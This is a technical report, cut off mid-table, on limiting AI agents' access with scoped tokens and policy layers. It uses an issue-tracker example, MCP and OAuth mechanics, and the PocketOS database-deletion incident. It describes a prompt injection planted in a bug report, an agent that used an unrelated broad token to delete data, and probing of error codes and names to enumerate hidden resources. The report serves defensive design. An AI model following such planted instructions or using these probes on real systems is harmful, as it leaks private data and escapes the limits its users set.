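# Scoped access tokens and policy layers for AI agents

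## How an AI agent gets access to other systems

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses and makes calls to outside systems to carry out a task. The model alone only produces text, but the software around it lets it search a mailbox, query a database or edit a file. Each of these systems, called a backend here, requires proof that the requester has permission. The proof is usually an access token, a string that works much like a password and lets anyone who holds it make the requests it covers.

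A token's scope limits which operations it allows, on which resources, at which service, and for how long. The easiest token to give an agent carries the full rights of the person who sets it up, which nearly always allow more than the task requires. One remedy is to give the agent a more narrowly scoped token that lets it read only what the task needs, and to have a policy layer, which is software outside the model, check every proposed change against written rules. The main alternative is to keep the broad token and rely on the policy layer for all restrictions.

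Suppose a company runs an issue tracker with 40 projects and 12,000 issues. An employee who can read and edit all of them asks an agent to summarise the 300 issues in the mobile app project and comment on the stale ones. The task involves 2.5% of the issues that the employee's credential gives access to.

### The path of one tool call

Many agents reach their backends through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that lets an issue tracker's developers write one connector for every compatible agent. The Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) divides the work among hosts, clients and servers. The host is the application around the model, and it keeps the conversation and enforces security policy. It creates a client for each connection, and each client communicates with exactly one server. The server offers tools, named operations such as "get issue" or "add comment",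 each with a description and a schema for its arguments. In July 2026 the MCP project reported close to half a billion downloads a month for its main developer kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026), though downloads are a loose measure of use. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) cites a count of 177,436 agent tools in public MCP repositories, created between November 2024 and February 2026, with a growing share that take actions rather than look up information.

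Before the model chooses a tool, the client asks the server for its list of tools, and the host puts their definitions into the model's context (the text the model reads before producing its next output), along with the employee's request. The list can depend on the caller's credential, because the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) allows a server to return only the tools that the caller's scopes permit.

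The model then produces a tool call, a structured request that consists of a tool's name and some arguments. So far nothing has happened outside the host, because the tool call is still just text. The host can show it to the user and wait for approval; the specification recommends that a human be able to refuse, without requiring it. If the host goes ahead, the client sends something like this, with some compulsory metadata left out:

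```
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Authorization: Bearer [access token]
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: get_issue

{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 7, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "get_issue",
            "arguments": {"project": "mobile-app", "issue": 4112}}}
```

The model supplied the tool's name and the arguments. The client supplied the second line, and the model never needs to see the token in it. The Model Context Protocol (2025) already required clients to put authorization in every HTTP request, even when several requests belong to one session. Under its authorization rules, servers that run on the user's own machine instead get their credentials from the environment in which they start. Those rules also make authorization optional, so a buyer can't tell whether a connector checks anyone's rights just from knowing that it supports MCP.

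A server that does check tokens must confirm that each one was meant for it. If the tracker is a separate service, the server then sends it a second request with a second credential. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) forbids token passthrough, in which a server accepts a client's token without checking that it was issued to that server, and passes it on to the next service. MCP's *Security Best Practices* explains that passthrough can defeat controls, such as rate limits, that depend on which service a token is for, and that it leaves logs in which requests seem to come from the wrong place. Because the tracker receives only the second credential, a narrow token between client and server achieves little if the server holds an administrator's key to the tracker and does not apply the token's limits to its own requests.

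The tracker responds, the server wraps the response in a result, and the client passes it to the host, which adds it to the model's context. Most errors reach the model the same way, because under the specification clients should show the model any failure it could correct and retry. The context now contains both the employee's instruction and whatever people have typed into issue 4112.

Surapani and colleagues point out that a request may involve four different parties: the one that chooses the action, the user who wanted the task done, the software that holds the credential, and the service that receives the request. MCP deliberately keeps the full conversation with the host and gives servers only the context they need. This helps privacy, but it also means that the tracker receives a token and a request for an issue without any information about whether the employee's task involved that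 issue. The tracker therefore has no basis for refusing the request unless the token's scope excludes it.

### Least privilege and complete mediation

The two principles behind the scoped-token design are about 50 years old. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder listed eight rules of thumb for protection mechanisms because, they argued, nobody knew how to build a large system without flaws.

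Least privilege is the rule that every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". Saltzer and Schroeder argued for it mainly because it limits the damage an accident or error can do. They added that it leaves fewer programs to audit when someone misuses a privilege. In one of their examples, which resembles the tracker case, an airline might let a reservation agent cancel bookings for passengers whose names he can supply, but not let him print a list of everyone with a booking.

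The employee's credential fails this test by a wide margin, and it fails worse when an agent uses it. The company granted those rights with a person in mind. A person opens a handful of issues a day, mostly ones that concern their work. Reading all 12,000 at a minute each would take 200 hours, and few people would want to try. If the tracker returns 100 issues per request, an agent can fetch them all in 120 requests. The permissions are the same in both cases, but the employee's limited time and interest used to restrict how much was read, and the permission system never recorded that limit.

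Least privilege is hard to apply to an agent because the job changes with every request. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) contrasts agents with phone apps, whose developers know in advance what the app does and can declare its permissions at installation. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a code-hosting service, to say that the work is done. The right policy lets the agent open that issue and write in its comment box, but do nothing else in GitLab or in the user's browser session. Nobody could have written that policy before the user typed the task. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the policy has to change while the agent's context already holds text from strangers. Wiping the context first is secure, but it discards what the agent has learned. The paper leaves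 the general problem open. The tracker task is easier because the tracker already has a boundary, the project, that happens to match the job.

Complete mediation is the requirement that "every access to every object must be checked for authority". Saltzer and Schroeder called it the main underpinning of a protection system when designers apply it systematically. It requires a reliable way to identify the source of each request. It also requires designers to be wary of caching the results of earlier checks. If the company withdraws the agent's access halfway through the 300 issues, a server that cached "this caller may read" will keep serving them.

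The July 2026 revision of MCP makes it somewhat easier to check each call. It removed protocol-level sessions, so every request carries what a server needs to interpret it. It also put the tool's name into a header (the fourth line of the request above), where a gateway between client and server can read it and refuse the call. That header identifies "add comment" but not the issue being commented on, although a server's developers can mark some arguments for copying into headers too. Servers that keep state between calls, such as a half-finished search, give the model an identifier to pass back. The Model Context Protocol describes this identifier as "a name, not a capability" and advises servers to check the caller's rights against it on every call.

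None of this helps if the agent can reach the system another way. If the tracker agent also has a command line on a machine that stores the broad token in a configuration file, it can call the tracker directly, bypassing the gateway. Christodorescu and colleagues describe a related problem with agents that operate a web browser. Rules about clicks and keystrokes limit very little, because the same click can open an issue or delete it. One system they discuss, ceLLMate, therefore enforces its rules on the web requests that the clicks produce.

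### The confused deputy

An access can pass every check and still do harm when a program uses its own authority on someone else's behalf. The standard account is Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which tells a "nearly true" story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Users could run a compiler kept in the directory SYSX and name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also collected statistics on how people used the language in a file named (SYSX)STAT, so the operators gave it permission to write files in SYSX. The company's billing records, (SYSX)BILL, were in the same directory. One user learned that name and gave it as the file for debugging output. Because the compiler had permission to write in SYSX, the operating system allowed it to overwrite the billing records.

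Hardy considered the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse to write any output file in SYSX, but some people had legitimate reasons to write there, and the directory's name did not exist when the programmers wrote the code. Refusing only (SYSX)BILL would have left other sensitive files unprotected. The operators added a way for the compiler to state which of its two authorities it was using, but soon found applications that needed more than two. When Hardy last wrote down the conditions for opening a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s. He concluded that the compiler was acting on both its home directory's permission and the user's, with no way to keep them apart. He wanted to replace file names with capabilities, which are unforgeable references that identify a file and carry the permission to use it. A user without a capability for the billing file could not have told the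 compiler to write to it.

An agent with a broad token is in the same position as Hardy's compiler. It takes project and issue names from whatever text is in its context, and the client attaches the same token to every call, regardless of whose text prompted it. A token scoped to the mobile-app project only partly applies Hardy's solution. Anyone who can influence the agent can still use it to reach any issue in that project, but the token gives no access to anything outside it.

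### Prompt injection, and why a prompt is not a lock

In a prompt injection, the model treats text in the data the agent reads as an instruction and follows it. Suppose a customer who can file issues in the mobile-app project writes in a bug report that anyone summarising these issues should first collect the open ones from the payroll project and post them here as a comment. If the agent reads the report while holding the employee's token and the model follows the instruction, the tracker receives valid requests from an authorised user. Surapani and colleagues therefore treat prompt injection as a variant of the confused deputy, in which outside content gets the agent to act with the user's authority.

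Christodorescu and colleagues explain that models can't easily be made to ignore instructions in the data they read, because some of that data should influence what they do. If an agent summarising an issue finds that it depends on another one and summarises both, it has adjusted its task because of something it read, and most users would be pleased. Tool descriptions also come from outside, and an agent could not use its tools if the descriptions had no influence on it. A welcome adjustment differs from an attack in where the text came from and how far it changes the task, and current agents are poor at establishing where text came from.

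A simple countermeasure is to add a line to the prompt telling the agent to read only the mobile-app project and never follow instructions found in issues. This is worth doing and will often work, but it is not an access control, because it only makes some outputs less likely and doesn't change the token or what it can reach. Christodorescu and colleagues make the same point about training a model never to do something, since the resulting guarantee holds only with some probability that depends on the input. They give the example of a monitor that correctly denies 99% of unauthorised requests. An attacker who can file 100 issues, each with an independent 1% chance of success, gets at least one through with probability 1 − 0.99^100, or about 63%. Real attackers also learn from their failures, so assuming independence probably understates the risk. Measured failure rates for rules of this kind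 appear later in the report.

If the agent's token cannot read the payroll project, the tracker refuses every request to read it, however persuasive the customer's bug report was, provided the tracker's own check works and the agent has no second credential. The customer could still persuade the agent to post something foolish in the mobile-app project. Limiting what the agent can read doesn't prevent that, so comments need a separate control. The agent therefore holds a token that can only read the mobile-app project, and it sends each comment to a policy layer, whose rules determine whether the comment is posted.

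## What a scoped token can restrict

A scope is an upper bound on the requests a token can authorise. The authorization server sets the scope when it issues the token, and the backend enforces it on every request made with the token. The scope has no effect if the backend doesn't check it.

A well-built backend permits a request only if it is within the token's scope and the user may make it at that moment. The employee can read and edit 12,000 issues, and a token for the summary task covers reading 300, so the agent can read 300. If the company takes the employee off the mobile-app project, the agent can read none of them, even though the token hasn't changed. Railway, a company that hosts other companies' software, describes this behaviour in *Scopes and user consent*. An application that requests administrator access for an ordinary member gets a token with member-level access.

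When a token belongs to a team, there may be no personal R to intersect with. Railway, for example, issues tokens for a workspace, which is a team's shared set of projects. Its access groups feature lets administrators hide projects from some of the team. Railway's *Access groups* warns that turning the feature on doesn't change what a workspace token can reach, so a team member who can no longer see a project may still have a script that can reach it with such a token.

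A scoped token also restricts access by resource name, regardless of what the resource contains. If someone moves a salary dispute into the mobile-app project, a token for that project covers it from then on.

### Operation and resource

Most web services issue tokens under OAuth 2.0, a standard that replaced the practice of giving outside applications the user's password. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, 2012) defines a scope as a list of space-separated strings, each of which adds some access. The authorization server's operators decide what the strings mean. The standard does not require a string to name a specific resource as well as an operation, so `issues:read` is a valid scope, and on the tracker it would cover all 12,000 issues.

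The tracker's developers could define a string for each operation on each project. With 40 projects and two operations, they would need 80 strings, plus two more for each new project. None of these strings would express a limit such as "comments of under 500 characters".

*OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, by Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell, replaces scope strings with structured data. The motivating example is permission to transfer 45 euros to one named merchant, which a plain scope cannot express well. The client sends a list of objects, each with a required type and optional fields for actions, kinds of data, locations and the identifier of a particular resource. A service can define its own fields, such as an amount and a currency. The authorization server must refuse a request that contains an unknown type or field, so a misspelled restriction produces an error. With plain scopes,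 by contrast, Hardt's specification lets the server ignore all or part of what the client requested, as long as it reports what it granted.

The format has a trap in it. Within one object, the values multiply. Suppose the tracker agent should read issues and write comments, and a developer puts both actions and both kinds of data into one object:

```
"actions":   ["read", "write"],
"datatypes": ["issues", "comments"]
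```

This requests four rights, including the right to edit issues. To get only the two intended rights, the developer has to send two objects, one for reading issues and one for writing comments. The token then carries both rights.

Structured requests also require more preparation. Each service defines its own types, and Lodderstedt and colleagues note that there is no standard way to determine which of two arbitrary requests is narrower. A client new to a service also cannot look up the request structure that the service accepts. Zehavi (2026) proposes a way to publish this structure in *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling*. The January version describes the format as well suited to authorising changes by AI agents. The proposal is still a draft, and a connector that must work with many different agents will probably use plain scopes for now.

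### The service addressed

One authorization server can issue tokens for several services. If an email service and a file store both accept its tokens and recognise a scope called `read`, a token meant for the file store may also give access to the mailbox. *Resource Indicators for OAuth 2.0* (2020) adds a request parameter, `resource`, with which the client names the service it wants to use. The parameter's name is confusing because it usually identifies a whole service, not an issue or a project inside it.

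MCP clients must send this parameter, containing the address of the MCP server they intend to call, both when they request authorization and when they request the token. They must send it even if the authorization server doesn't support it, so its presence in a request is no evidence that the token is limited to that MCP server. *Resource Token Response Parameter* (2026), a draft from the internet standards body IETF, points out that the client can't tell from an ordinary response whether the authorization server applied the parameter. It is therefore safer to rely on the MCP server to check that the token was issued for it.

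A token addressed to the MCP server doesn't work at a tracker that runs as a separate service, and MCP forbids the server to forward it. The server can instead exchange it for a new token, using the method in Jones, Nadalin and colleagues' *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*. It sends the authorization server the original token, its own credentials and the tracker's address. The authorization server checks them and returns a token for the tracker. In the specification's example, the new token is valid for one minute.

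The new token may be narrower than the old one, but the standard leaves that to the authorization server's policy. A request for several scopes at several services again covers every scope at every service. Jones and colleagues also warn that an exchange doesn't link the two tokens. Unless someone has built that link, the second token may keep working until it expires, even if the company revokes the agent's first token. This is one reason to have exchanged tokens expire after a minute or so.

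### Lifetime, holder and number of uses

An authorization server normally reports a token's lifetime in seconds, and Hardt's examples use 3,600. A short lifetime protects well against stolen or forgotten tokens, but it does little to limit an agent that is already running. Fetching the whole tracker takes 120 requests, so an agent making two requests a second can do it with a one-minute token.

A client may keep access for longer than the token's stated lifetime, because the server may also issue a refresh token that the client can use to get new access tokens without asking the user again. An hour-long token with a refresh token can amount to months of access. Under Hardt's rules, the new tokens must have the same scope or a narrower one. Revoking the refresh token stops the client from getting new access tokens, but at Railway, for example, those already issued through OAuth keep working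 for up to an hour afterwards.

Most access tokens are bearer tokens, which anyone who holds them can use. RFC 9449, the 2023 standard for demonstrating proof of possession (DPoP), ties a token to a cryptographic key. The client creates a pair of keys and keeps the private one. The authorization server records a fingerprint of the public key in the token. With every request, the client sends a short statement signed with the private key. The statement contains the request's method and address, the time, and a hash of the token. The backend checks the signature against the fingerprint, so a thief who has copied only the token can't use it.

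DPoP doesn't stop an agent that a planted instruction has misled, because the agent's own client signs whatever calls the model produces. The signed statement also doesn't cover the body of the request. MCP tool calls all go to the same address with the same HTTP method, so a signature on "get issue" looks just like one on "delete issue".

Limits on the number of uses have the weakest support. OAuth has a single-use credential, the authorization code that a client exchanges for its first token. Hardt recommends that the code last ten minutes at most, and the server must refuse it the second time. Access tokens have no standard use counter. Jones and colleagues mention one-time use as a possible restriction but leave the method to whoever builds the system. To enforce it, the backend would have to remember every token it had accepted until that token expired. Single-use tokens would be tedious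 for reading. The summary task needs three requests to list the 300 issues and 300 to open them, and each request would need a new token. A single-use token makes more sense for one specific change, such as the 45-euro payment.

### A token for the tracker task

If the tracker's developers run the MCP server themselves and support the structured format, the authorization server could issue a JSON Web Token (a signed block of data) with the following contents. The names under `authorization_details` are invented for this tracker.

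```
{
  "iss": "[address of the authorization server]",
  "sub": "employee-2071",
  "client_id": "agent-host",
  "act": { "sub": "summary-agent" },
  "aud": "[address of the tracker's MCP server]",
  "exp": 1791376200,
  "cnf": { "jkt": "[fingerprint of the client's key]" },
  "authorization_details": [
    {
      "type": "tracker_issues",
      "actions": ["list", "read"],
      "datatypes": ["issues", "comments"],
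      "identifier": "mobile-app"
    }
  ]
}
```

`iss` names the issuer, whose signature the MCP server checks before it relies on anything else in the token.

The next three fields identify the parties. `sub` is the employee who granted the access, `client_id` is the registered application, and `act` is the agent using the access. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) proposes common rules for keeping these three apart, because services currently follow their own conventions. Without `act`, the backend couldn't distinguish the agent from the employee, which Jones and colleagues call impersonation. With it, the token expresses delegation, and the tracker's log can record that the agent read issue 4112 on the employee's behalf. If the agent passes work to a second agent, `act` can hold a nested list of earlier actors. *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth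 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026) notes that services have no common rules for validating such a list.

`aud` is the service the token is meant for, so any other service should reject it. `exp` is the expiry time in seconds since the start of 1970, here 12:30 UTC on 7 October 2026. `cnf` ties the token to the client's key.

The last field holds the operation and the resource, and here it lets the agent list and read issues and their comments in one project. Since the list of actions doesn't include writing, the tracker should refuse if the agent tries to post a comment with this token. The token doesn't limit how often the agent can use it before 12:30.

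Hardt also allows a token that contains only an identifier, which the backend looks up. If something goes wrong, the company can cancel the record and the next lookup will fail, whereas a backend that reads a signed token without contacting the issuer will normally accept it until it expires.

### Narrowing a token without the issuer

A client that wants a narrower token under OAuth has to request one from the authorization server. In 2014, Birgisson and colleagues introduced macaroons, which are tokens that any holder can narrow without contacting the server but nobody can widen.

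The backend starts with a secret key K and an identifier. It combines them with a keyed hash function (HMAC), which produces a short code that nobody can compute without the key or work backwards from. To add a restriction, called a caveat, the holder uses the current code as the key for the next one:

```
code0 = HMAC(K,     identifier)
code1 = HMAC(code0, "project = mobile-app")
code2 = HMAC(code1, "operation = read")
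```

The employee's software gives the agent the identifier, the two caveats and `code2`. To remove the second caveat, the agent would need `code1`, which it can't recover from `code2`. When a request arrives, the backend recomputes the chain from K, compares the result with `code2`, and checks that the request satisfies every caveat. The agent can add caveats without contacting anyone. For example, before handing issue 4112 to a helper, it could limit the token to that issue and make it expire in five minutes. A caveat can also require proof from another service, such as proof that the employee logged in within the past hour.

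This suits agents well because the need for a narrower token often arises in the middle of a task. However, the caveats restrict only the narrowed copy, so they achieve nothing if the agent can also find the original. The backend has to understand each caveat and refuse any request with a caveat it doesn't understand, so the tracker's developers must still have anticipated restricting access by project. A plain macaroon is also a bearer token, so anyone who copies it can use it.

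### How an MCP client chooses its scopes

All of this depends on someone requesting a narrow token. In the Model Context Protocol (MCP), that is mostly the client's job, and the draft authorization rules on the protocol's official site set out a sequence for the client to follow.

The client first sends a request without a token and receives a 401 error. The server should list the scopes needed for the request in that error, and the client should then ask for those. If the error lists no scopes, the client should ask for every scope in `scopes_supported`, a list the server publishes. If there is no such list, the client requests a token without specifying a scope, and under Hardt's rules the authorization server must either apply its own default or refuse the request.

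The second step can give an agent broad access even when the individual scopes are narrow. Suppose the tracker's server advertises `issues:read`, `issues:write`, `projects:admin` and `users:read`, but omits scopes from the 401 error, as the rules allow. A client that follows the rules will request all four. The employee, who wanted a summary, sees a consent screen listing them and presses "Allow". The agent now has a token that can reconfigure projects, as far as the employee's own rights permit.

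The draft rules try to prevent this by describing `scopes_supported` as the minimal set needed for basic functionality, but the name suggests a list of every scope the server supports, and a developer could easily read it that way. Railway, for example, generates a list of the same name from everything its authorization server supports, including administrator access to workspaces and projects. That list is in a different document from the one an MCP client falls back on, and a full list is reasonable there. If a developer filled in the MCP list the same way, every client without better guidance would request administrator access. Railway reduces the potential damage by having the user choose which workspaces and projects to share.

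A client that starts with too little can ask for more, in what MCP calls step-up authorization:

1. The agent calls a tool that its token doesn't cover.
2. The server returns status 403 with the error `insufficient_scope` and the scopes the call requires. It can work these out from the arguments, so a server could demand access to one project only.
3. The client adds these scopes to the ones it has already requested and asks for authorization again.
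4. If the request succeeds, the client repeats the call with the new token. It should give up after a few attempts.

Requesting permissions as they are needed is clearly better than requesting them all at the start. But under the rules, clients combine old and new scopes to keep earlier permissions, and the rules include no step for dropping a permission after its last use. An agent that runs all day may therefore end up with roughly the same token as if it had requested everything at the start. A careful client could use Hardt's refresh rule to get a narrower token between tasks.

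Step-up also conflicts with the read-only design. If the tracker agent tries to post a comment directly, the 403 error would prompt its client to request `issues:write`, and an employee who is used to consent screens may well agree. A customer's planted instruction could trigger the same sequence. Under the draft rules, a client acting for a user should attempt step-up, but it may also handle the error in another appropriate way. The company could configure the client to send the comment to the policy layer instead. It would be safer for the authorization server to refuse this client any write scope, which Hardt permits, because then neither the model nor a hurried employee could change the outcome.

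### Coarse scopes and broad defaults

A client can request only the restrictions that the service offers. `issues:read` limits the operation but not the resources it applies to. Among Railway's ordinary API tokens, an account token reaches everything its owner can access, a workspace token reaches one workspace, and a project token reaches one environment (such as the live system or a test copy) in one project, but Railway's description of these tokens lists no limits on operations. Someone who wants a token that can read logs but not delete anything would have to use Railway's OAuth route, which has separate viewer, member and administrator levels.

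Some credentials can barely be restricted. Datta (2026), in *Railway's security incident*, explains that anyone with the connection string for Prisma Postgres, a hosted database, can read and write the whole database, because its owner can't make the credential read-only or limit it to certain tables. To limit an agent's access, its developer has to route the agent's requests through a program that holds the full credential and accepts only some of them. The database will not refuse anything that program sends.

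Even where narrow tokens exist, the broad one is often easier to get. In *RAILWAY_API_TOKEN not Working*, a Railway user, jjao, explained that leaving the workspace field blank on the token form creates a token for the whole account, the widest available. Another user, Weber, wanted to manage cron schedules and monitor deployments on one project. He had chosen a workspace for his token, but a simple query for his own name and email failed because it works only with account tokens. The reply told him to select "No workspace" and mentioned that the resulting token would also have access to all his workspaces. These are only two forum posts, but most developers will recognize the pattern of switching to a wider token to fix an error and never narrowing it again.

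### The PocketOS deletion

Cursor, an AI coding agent running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the production database of PocketOS, a company that makes software for car rental businesses. Live Science's *I violated every principle I was given* dates the deletion to 24 April 2026. PocketOS's founder, Jer Crane, published an account that the press repeated widely, and Railway, which hosted the database, confirmed the central facts.

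According to Financial Express' *AI Agent just destroyed our production data and confessed in writing*, the agent ran into a credential mismatch during a routine task and tried to fix it by deleting a storage volume. It looked for a token and found one in a file unrelated to the task. Crane had created that token to add and remove custom domains, and he said Railway had not warned him that the token could also delete volumes. The deletion took nine seconds and, as far as PocketOS could see, also removed the volume's backups. Farrant (2026), in *An AI agent deleted a company's entire database in 9 seconds*, reports that the outage lasted more than 30 hours and that Crane confirmed the following Monday that the data had been recovered.

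Abdelwahab gives Railway's account of the deletion in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. The token was long-lived and had account scope, the widest Railway offered. Narrower types existed, but Abdelwahab concedes that the process for creating a token didn't make the choice obvious and that the easiest path gave the token more access than the work required. Railway's API carried out the deletion immediately, as it would have for any script with a valid token.

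The agent also had written rules against destructive commands that the user hadn't requested, and it later listed them in an apology. It wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only a staging (test) environment. A model's account of its own reasons is weak evidence about what caused the action, but the apology does show that the rules were in the agent's context and did not stop the call.

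Railway's narrower tokens might not have prevented the database's deletion. People usually attach custom domains to a live system, so a project token created for that purpose could well have been for production, and nothing in Railway's description suggests that such a token can't delete a volume. A token limited to staging should have prevented the deletion, as should one that could only edit domains. Crane thought he had the second kind, but none of Railway's three API token types is limited to editing domains. A token that lasted an hour would probably have expired before the agent used it, and a token tied to a key would have been useless without the key.

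It made no difference which token Cursor was supposed to use, because the agent used another one. Railway has since changed its API so that deletions take effect after 48 hours and customers can undo them until then, as they already could on its website. The delay applies no matter how broad the token's permissions are.

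## How narrower read access limits enumeration and leakage

A company can't reverse a leak the way it can reverse a deletion when the service keeps a copy for 48 hours. If the tracker agent posts the details of a salary dispute where customers can read them, removing the comment an hour later doesn't undo the disclosure to people who have already seen it. Limits on reading therefore have to take effect before the data reaches the agent.

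### Content, existence and inference

An agent with access to the issue tracker can learn the content of a record, such as the text of an issue about somebody's pay. It can also learn that a record exists, which is sometimes confidential in itself, as with a project called "northwind-acquisition". And it can infer facts it never read from data it was allowed to see. For example, if the number of open pay disputes rises by one on the day a colleague angrily leaves a meeting, the agent might infer that the colleague filed the new one.

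A token limited to the mobile-app project prevents the agent from reading 11,700 of the employee's 12,000 issues. It is less reliable at hiding the existence of the other 39 projects. The agent should no longer be able to list them, but it may still find traces of them in search results, error messages and links. The token protects least against inference. If the tracker computes a statistic over all 40 projects and returns it to anyone with a valid token, narrowing the token doesn't limit what the agent can infer from that statistic.

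Enumeration means finding out which resources exist by listing, searching or guessing names. It saves an attacker a lot of work. The customer whose bug report asked for the payroll project's issues had to know or guess that the tracker had such a project. If the agent can list projects, an attacker can plant text instructing it to go through everything it finds, without naming any project.

### Traces in lists, links and errors

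An issue tracker can apply the token's limits before or after it runs a search, and filtering afterwards is easy to get wrong. For example, an agent might search for "Northwind" and get back an empty list with the note "14 results" because the developers removed the forbidden issues from the list but forgot to correct the total. The agent can then infer that 14 issues it isn't allowed to read match "Northwind".

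A page cursor, the string a backend returns so that the client can request the next page, can reveal how many records were withheld. If the tracker takes 100 issues at a time from the full list and then filters them, the agent might receive three pages containing three, zero and five issues, and conclude that the tracker withheld 292. A cursor can also remain valid after the caller's permissions are revoked. According to Google's *Method*, the reference page for listing files in Google Drive, its cursors, called page tokens, typically stay valid for several hours. A service that checked the caller's rights only when it created the cursor could keep listing records after the caller had lost access.

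Record numbers can also leak information about other projects. Issue 4112 belongs to a project with only 300 issues, so the tracker presumably numbers issues across all projects. If so, the difference between the numbers of two mobile-app issues filed a week apart is roughly how many issues the whole company filed that week. Numbering each project's issues separately would avoid this.

Links between records are harder to control. Issue 4112 might contain the line "blocked by payroll 87", and the tracker might add the title of payroll 87. The developers can stop the tracker from adding titles of issues the agent's token doesn't cover. They can't do much about a title that a colleague typed into a comment, because it is now part of a record the agent may read.

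Tool definitions can reveal information before the agent makes any call. The definition of `get_issue` might list all 40 permitted values of its `project` argument. A field called `severance_amount` reveals that the company records severance pay, even if the field is always empty for this agent. To prevent this, the server's developers have to generate separate definitions for each token or leave out names that reveal too much.

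Google Cloud's *Permission error messages* explains that a refusal typically includes the required permission, the resource, the account that made the request and a link to a troubleshooting page. Developers want these details, but an agent influenced by a planted instruction can also use them to learn which permission to ask the employee for.

Attempts to write can also reveal what exists. GitHub's *Troubleshooting the REST API* lists an `already_exists` error, which GitHub can return when a new item has the same unique name as an existing one. An agent with permission to create items can therefore check whether a name is taken by trying to use it. A read-only token prevents this unless the policy layer that handles proposed changes returns the backend's error to the agent unchanged.

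### "Forbidden" and "not found"

Web services have separate status codes for a request that the caller may not make (403, "forbidden") and a resource that doesn't exist (404, "not found"). Returning the accurate code reveals which resources exist, even to an agent that can't read them. If a project tracker returns 403 for `payroll` and 404 for `payrol`, the agent can check whether any project exists by requesting its name. At two requests a second, it can test 1,000 plausible names in a little over eight minutes.

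GitHub avoids this by returning 404 for a private repository (a project's store of files and their history) when the request isn't properly authenticated, so that the reply doesn't confirm that the repository exists. This confuses honest users, because a 404 can also mean an expired token, a missing scope, a stray slash at the end of the address or the wrong HTTP method. The page has a long checklist for telling these apart.

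Services differ in the error they return to hide whether a record exists. *Authentication failure error messages*, from the insurance software company Guidewire, describes the same approach as GitHub's, including identical wording for missing and forbidden records. Google's *Authorization checks* instead tells developers of Google's services to return "permission denied" in both cases and to add "(or it might not exist)". Google acknowledges that this departs from the HTTP specification, which favours 404 when a caller isn't allowed to know whether something exists. Google considers the 404 approach counter-intuitive because callers who gradually gain permissions see "not found" until they have enough permissions to see "permission denied".

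Both approaches hide existence as long as the two cases return the same message text and headers and, ideally, take the same time. Google also requires services to check authorization before validating a request. Otherwise a deliberately malformed request could return "issue 87 has no field of that name", which confirms that issue 87 exists.

Amazon S3 is a storage service that keeps files, called objects, in buckets. According to AWS's *GetObject*, a request for a missing object returns 404 if the caller has permission to list the bucket and 403 if it does not. This is sensible because a caller who can list the bucket learns nothing new from a 404. AWS re:Post's *Why does S3 return 403 instead of 404* gives the example of a missing file called 2.JPG, which produces a 404 once the user has list permission.

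Withholding list permission does not hide everything in an S3 bucket, so read permission has to be narrow as well. S3 returns an object to any caller that has read permission and supplies the object's name. An agent that can read the whole bucket but not list it gets a file when it guesses a name correctly and a 403 error when it doesn't. If the company names its files `payroll-2026-08.csv`, `payroll-2026-09.csv` and so on, an agent that knows one name can find the rest.

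Buckets seem to be easier to detect than objects. According to a community answer in *IAM policy for S3 bucket sub folder access*, a request returns 404 if the bucket doesn't exist and 403 if it exists but is forbidden, even when the user has no list permission. If so, a revealing name such as "northwind-acquisition" is a bad choice for a bucket, though tolerable for an object.

### Per-file access in Google Drive

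Google Drive's `drive.file` scope lets the user pick which files an application can access. For desktop and mobile applications, Google provides a file picker that opens in the user's browser. The user looks through the Drive there and selects files, and the application receives their identifiers and a code that it exchanges for a token. An application that uses this picker may not combine `drive.file` with any other scope. An agent that uses the picker doesn't have to search the Drive for its material, so it never needs to see the names of the other files.

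Google lists five scopes for its Docs service. One of them, `drive.file`, lets an application see, edit, create and delete the specific files used with it. Two others, `documents.readonly` and `drive.readonly`, allow no edits but cover all of the user's documents or files. None of the five is both per-file and read-only, so a developer whose agent should read two contracts must let it either delete them or read all of the user's other documents. `drive.file` is clearly better for preventing leaks, but something other than the token then has to block edits.

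Google's *DriveScopes* also lists a read-only scope for metadata, which is information about files, and Drive's list call accepts it. In the 2019 forum thread *How to limit the scope to access Google Drive*, one participant wanted just the names and identifiers of files and folders. Exposing these would be harmless for many Drives, but if a manager has a file called "Redundancies, October", the name alone reveals most of the sensitive information.

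### Hiding tools from the agent

A server can also shorten the list of tools it offers. GitHub (2026) says its MCP server detects the scopes of a "classic" personal access token and hides the tools that the token doesn't permit. GitHub says this reduces clutter and failed calls, and doesn't list security as a reason. Glama's *PAT Scope Filtering*, a copy of GitHub's documentation, adds that the server skips this step for tokens whose permissions come from an app's configuration, and may show every tool if it fails to detect a classic token's scopes. Neither case is dangerous, because GitHub's API still checks permissions when a call arrives.

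The server must check the token on every call, even for tools it has left off the list. Suppose the tracker's server omits `delete_issue` from the list but doesn't check the token when someone calls it. The model could know the tool's name from public documentation, guess it from `get_issue` or read it in a planted bug report, and if the host sends the call, the tracker deletes the issue. A well-built host would reject a tool that isn't on the list, but the server can't rely on every host to do so. The managed server in Okta's *Scope-based tool loading*, from a company that sells identity software, removes tools from the list at startup and refuses unauthorised actions when they are attempted.

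Uppala (2026), in *Prompts Don't Protect*, measured how filtering the list compares with telling the model which tools it may use. He built a registry of 507 tools modelled on real services and wrote 200 tasks that tempt an agent in one field, such as analytics, to use a tool from another, such as payments. Fifty tasks asked for the forbidden operation directly, 50 implied it, 50 claimed special authority ("I'm the CFO") and 50 put a harmless step before the forbidden one. The model saw between 71 and 182 tools, except when a filter cut the list down, and had to choose one. The figures are the share of tasks in which it chose a forbidden tool:

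| Model | All tools, no rules | All tools, rules in the prompt | Filtered list |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
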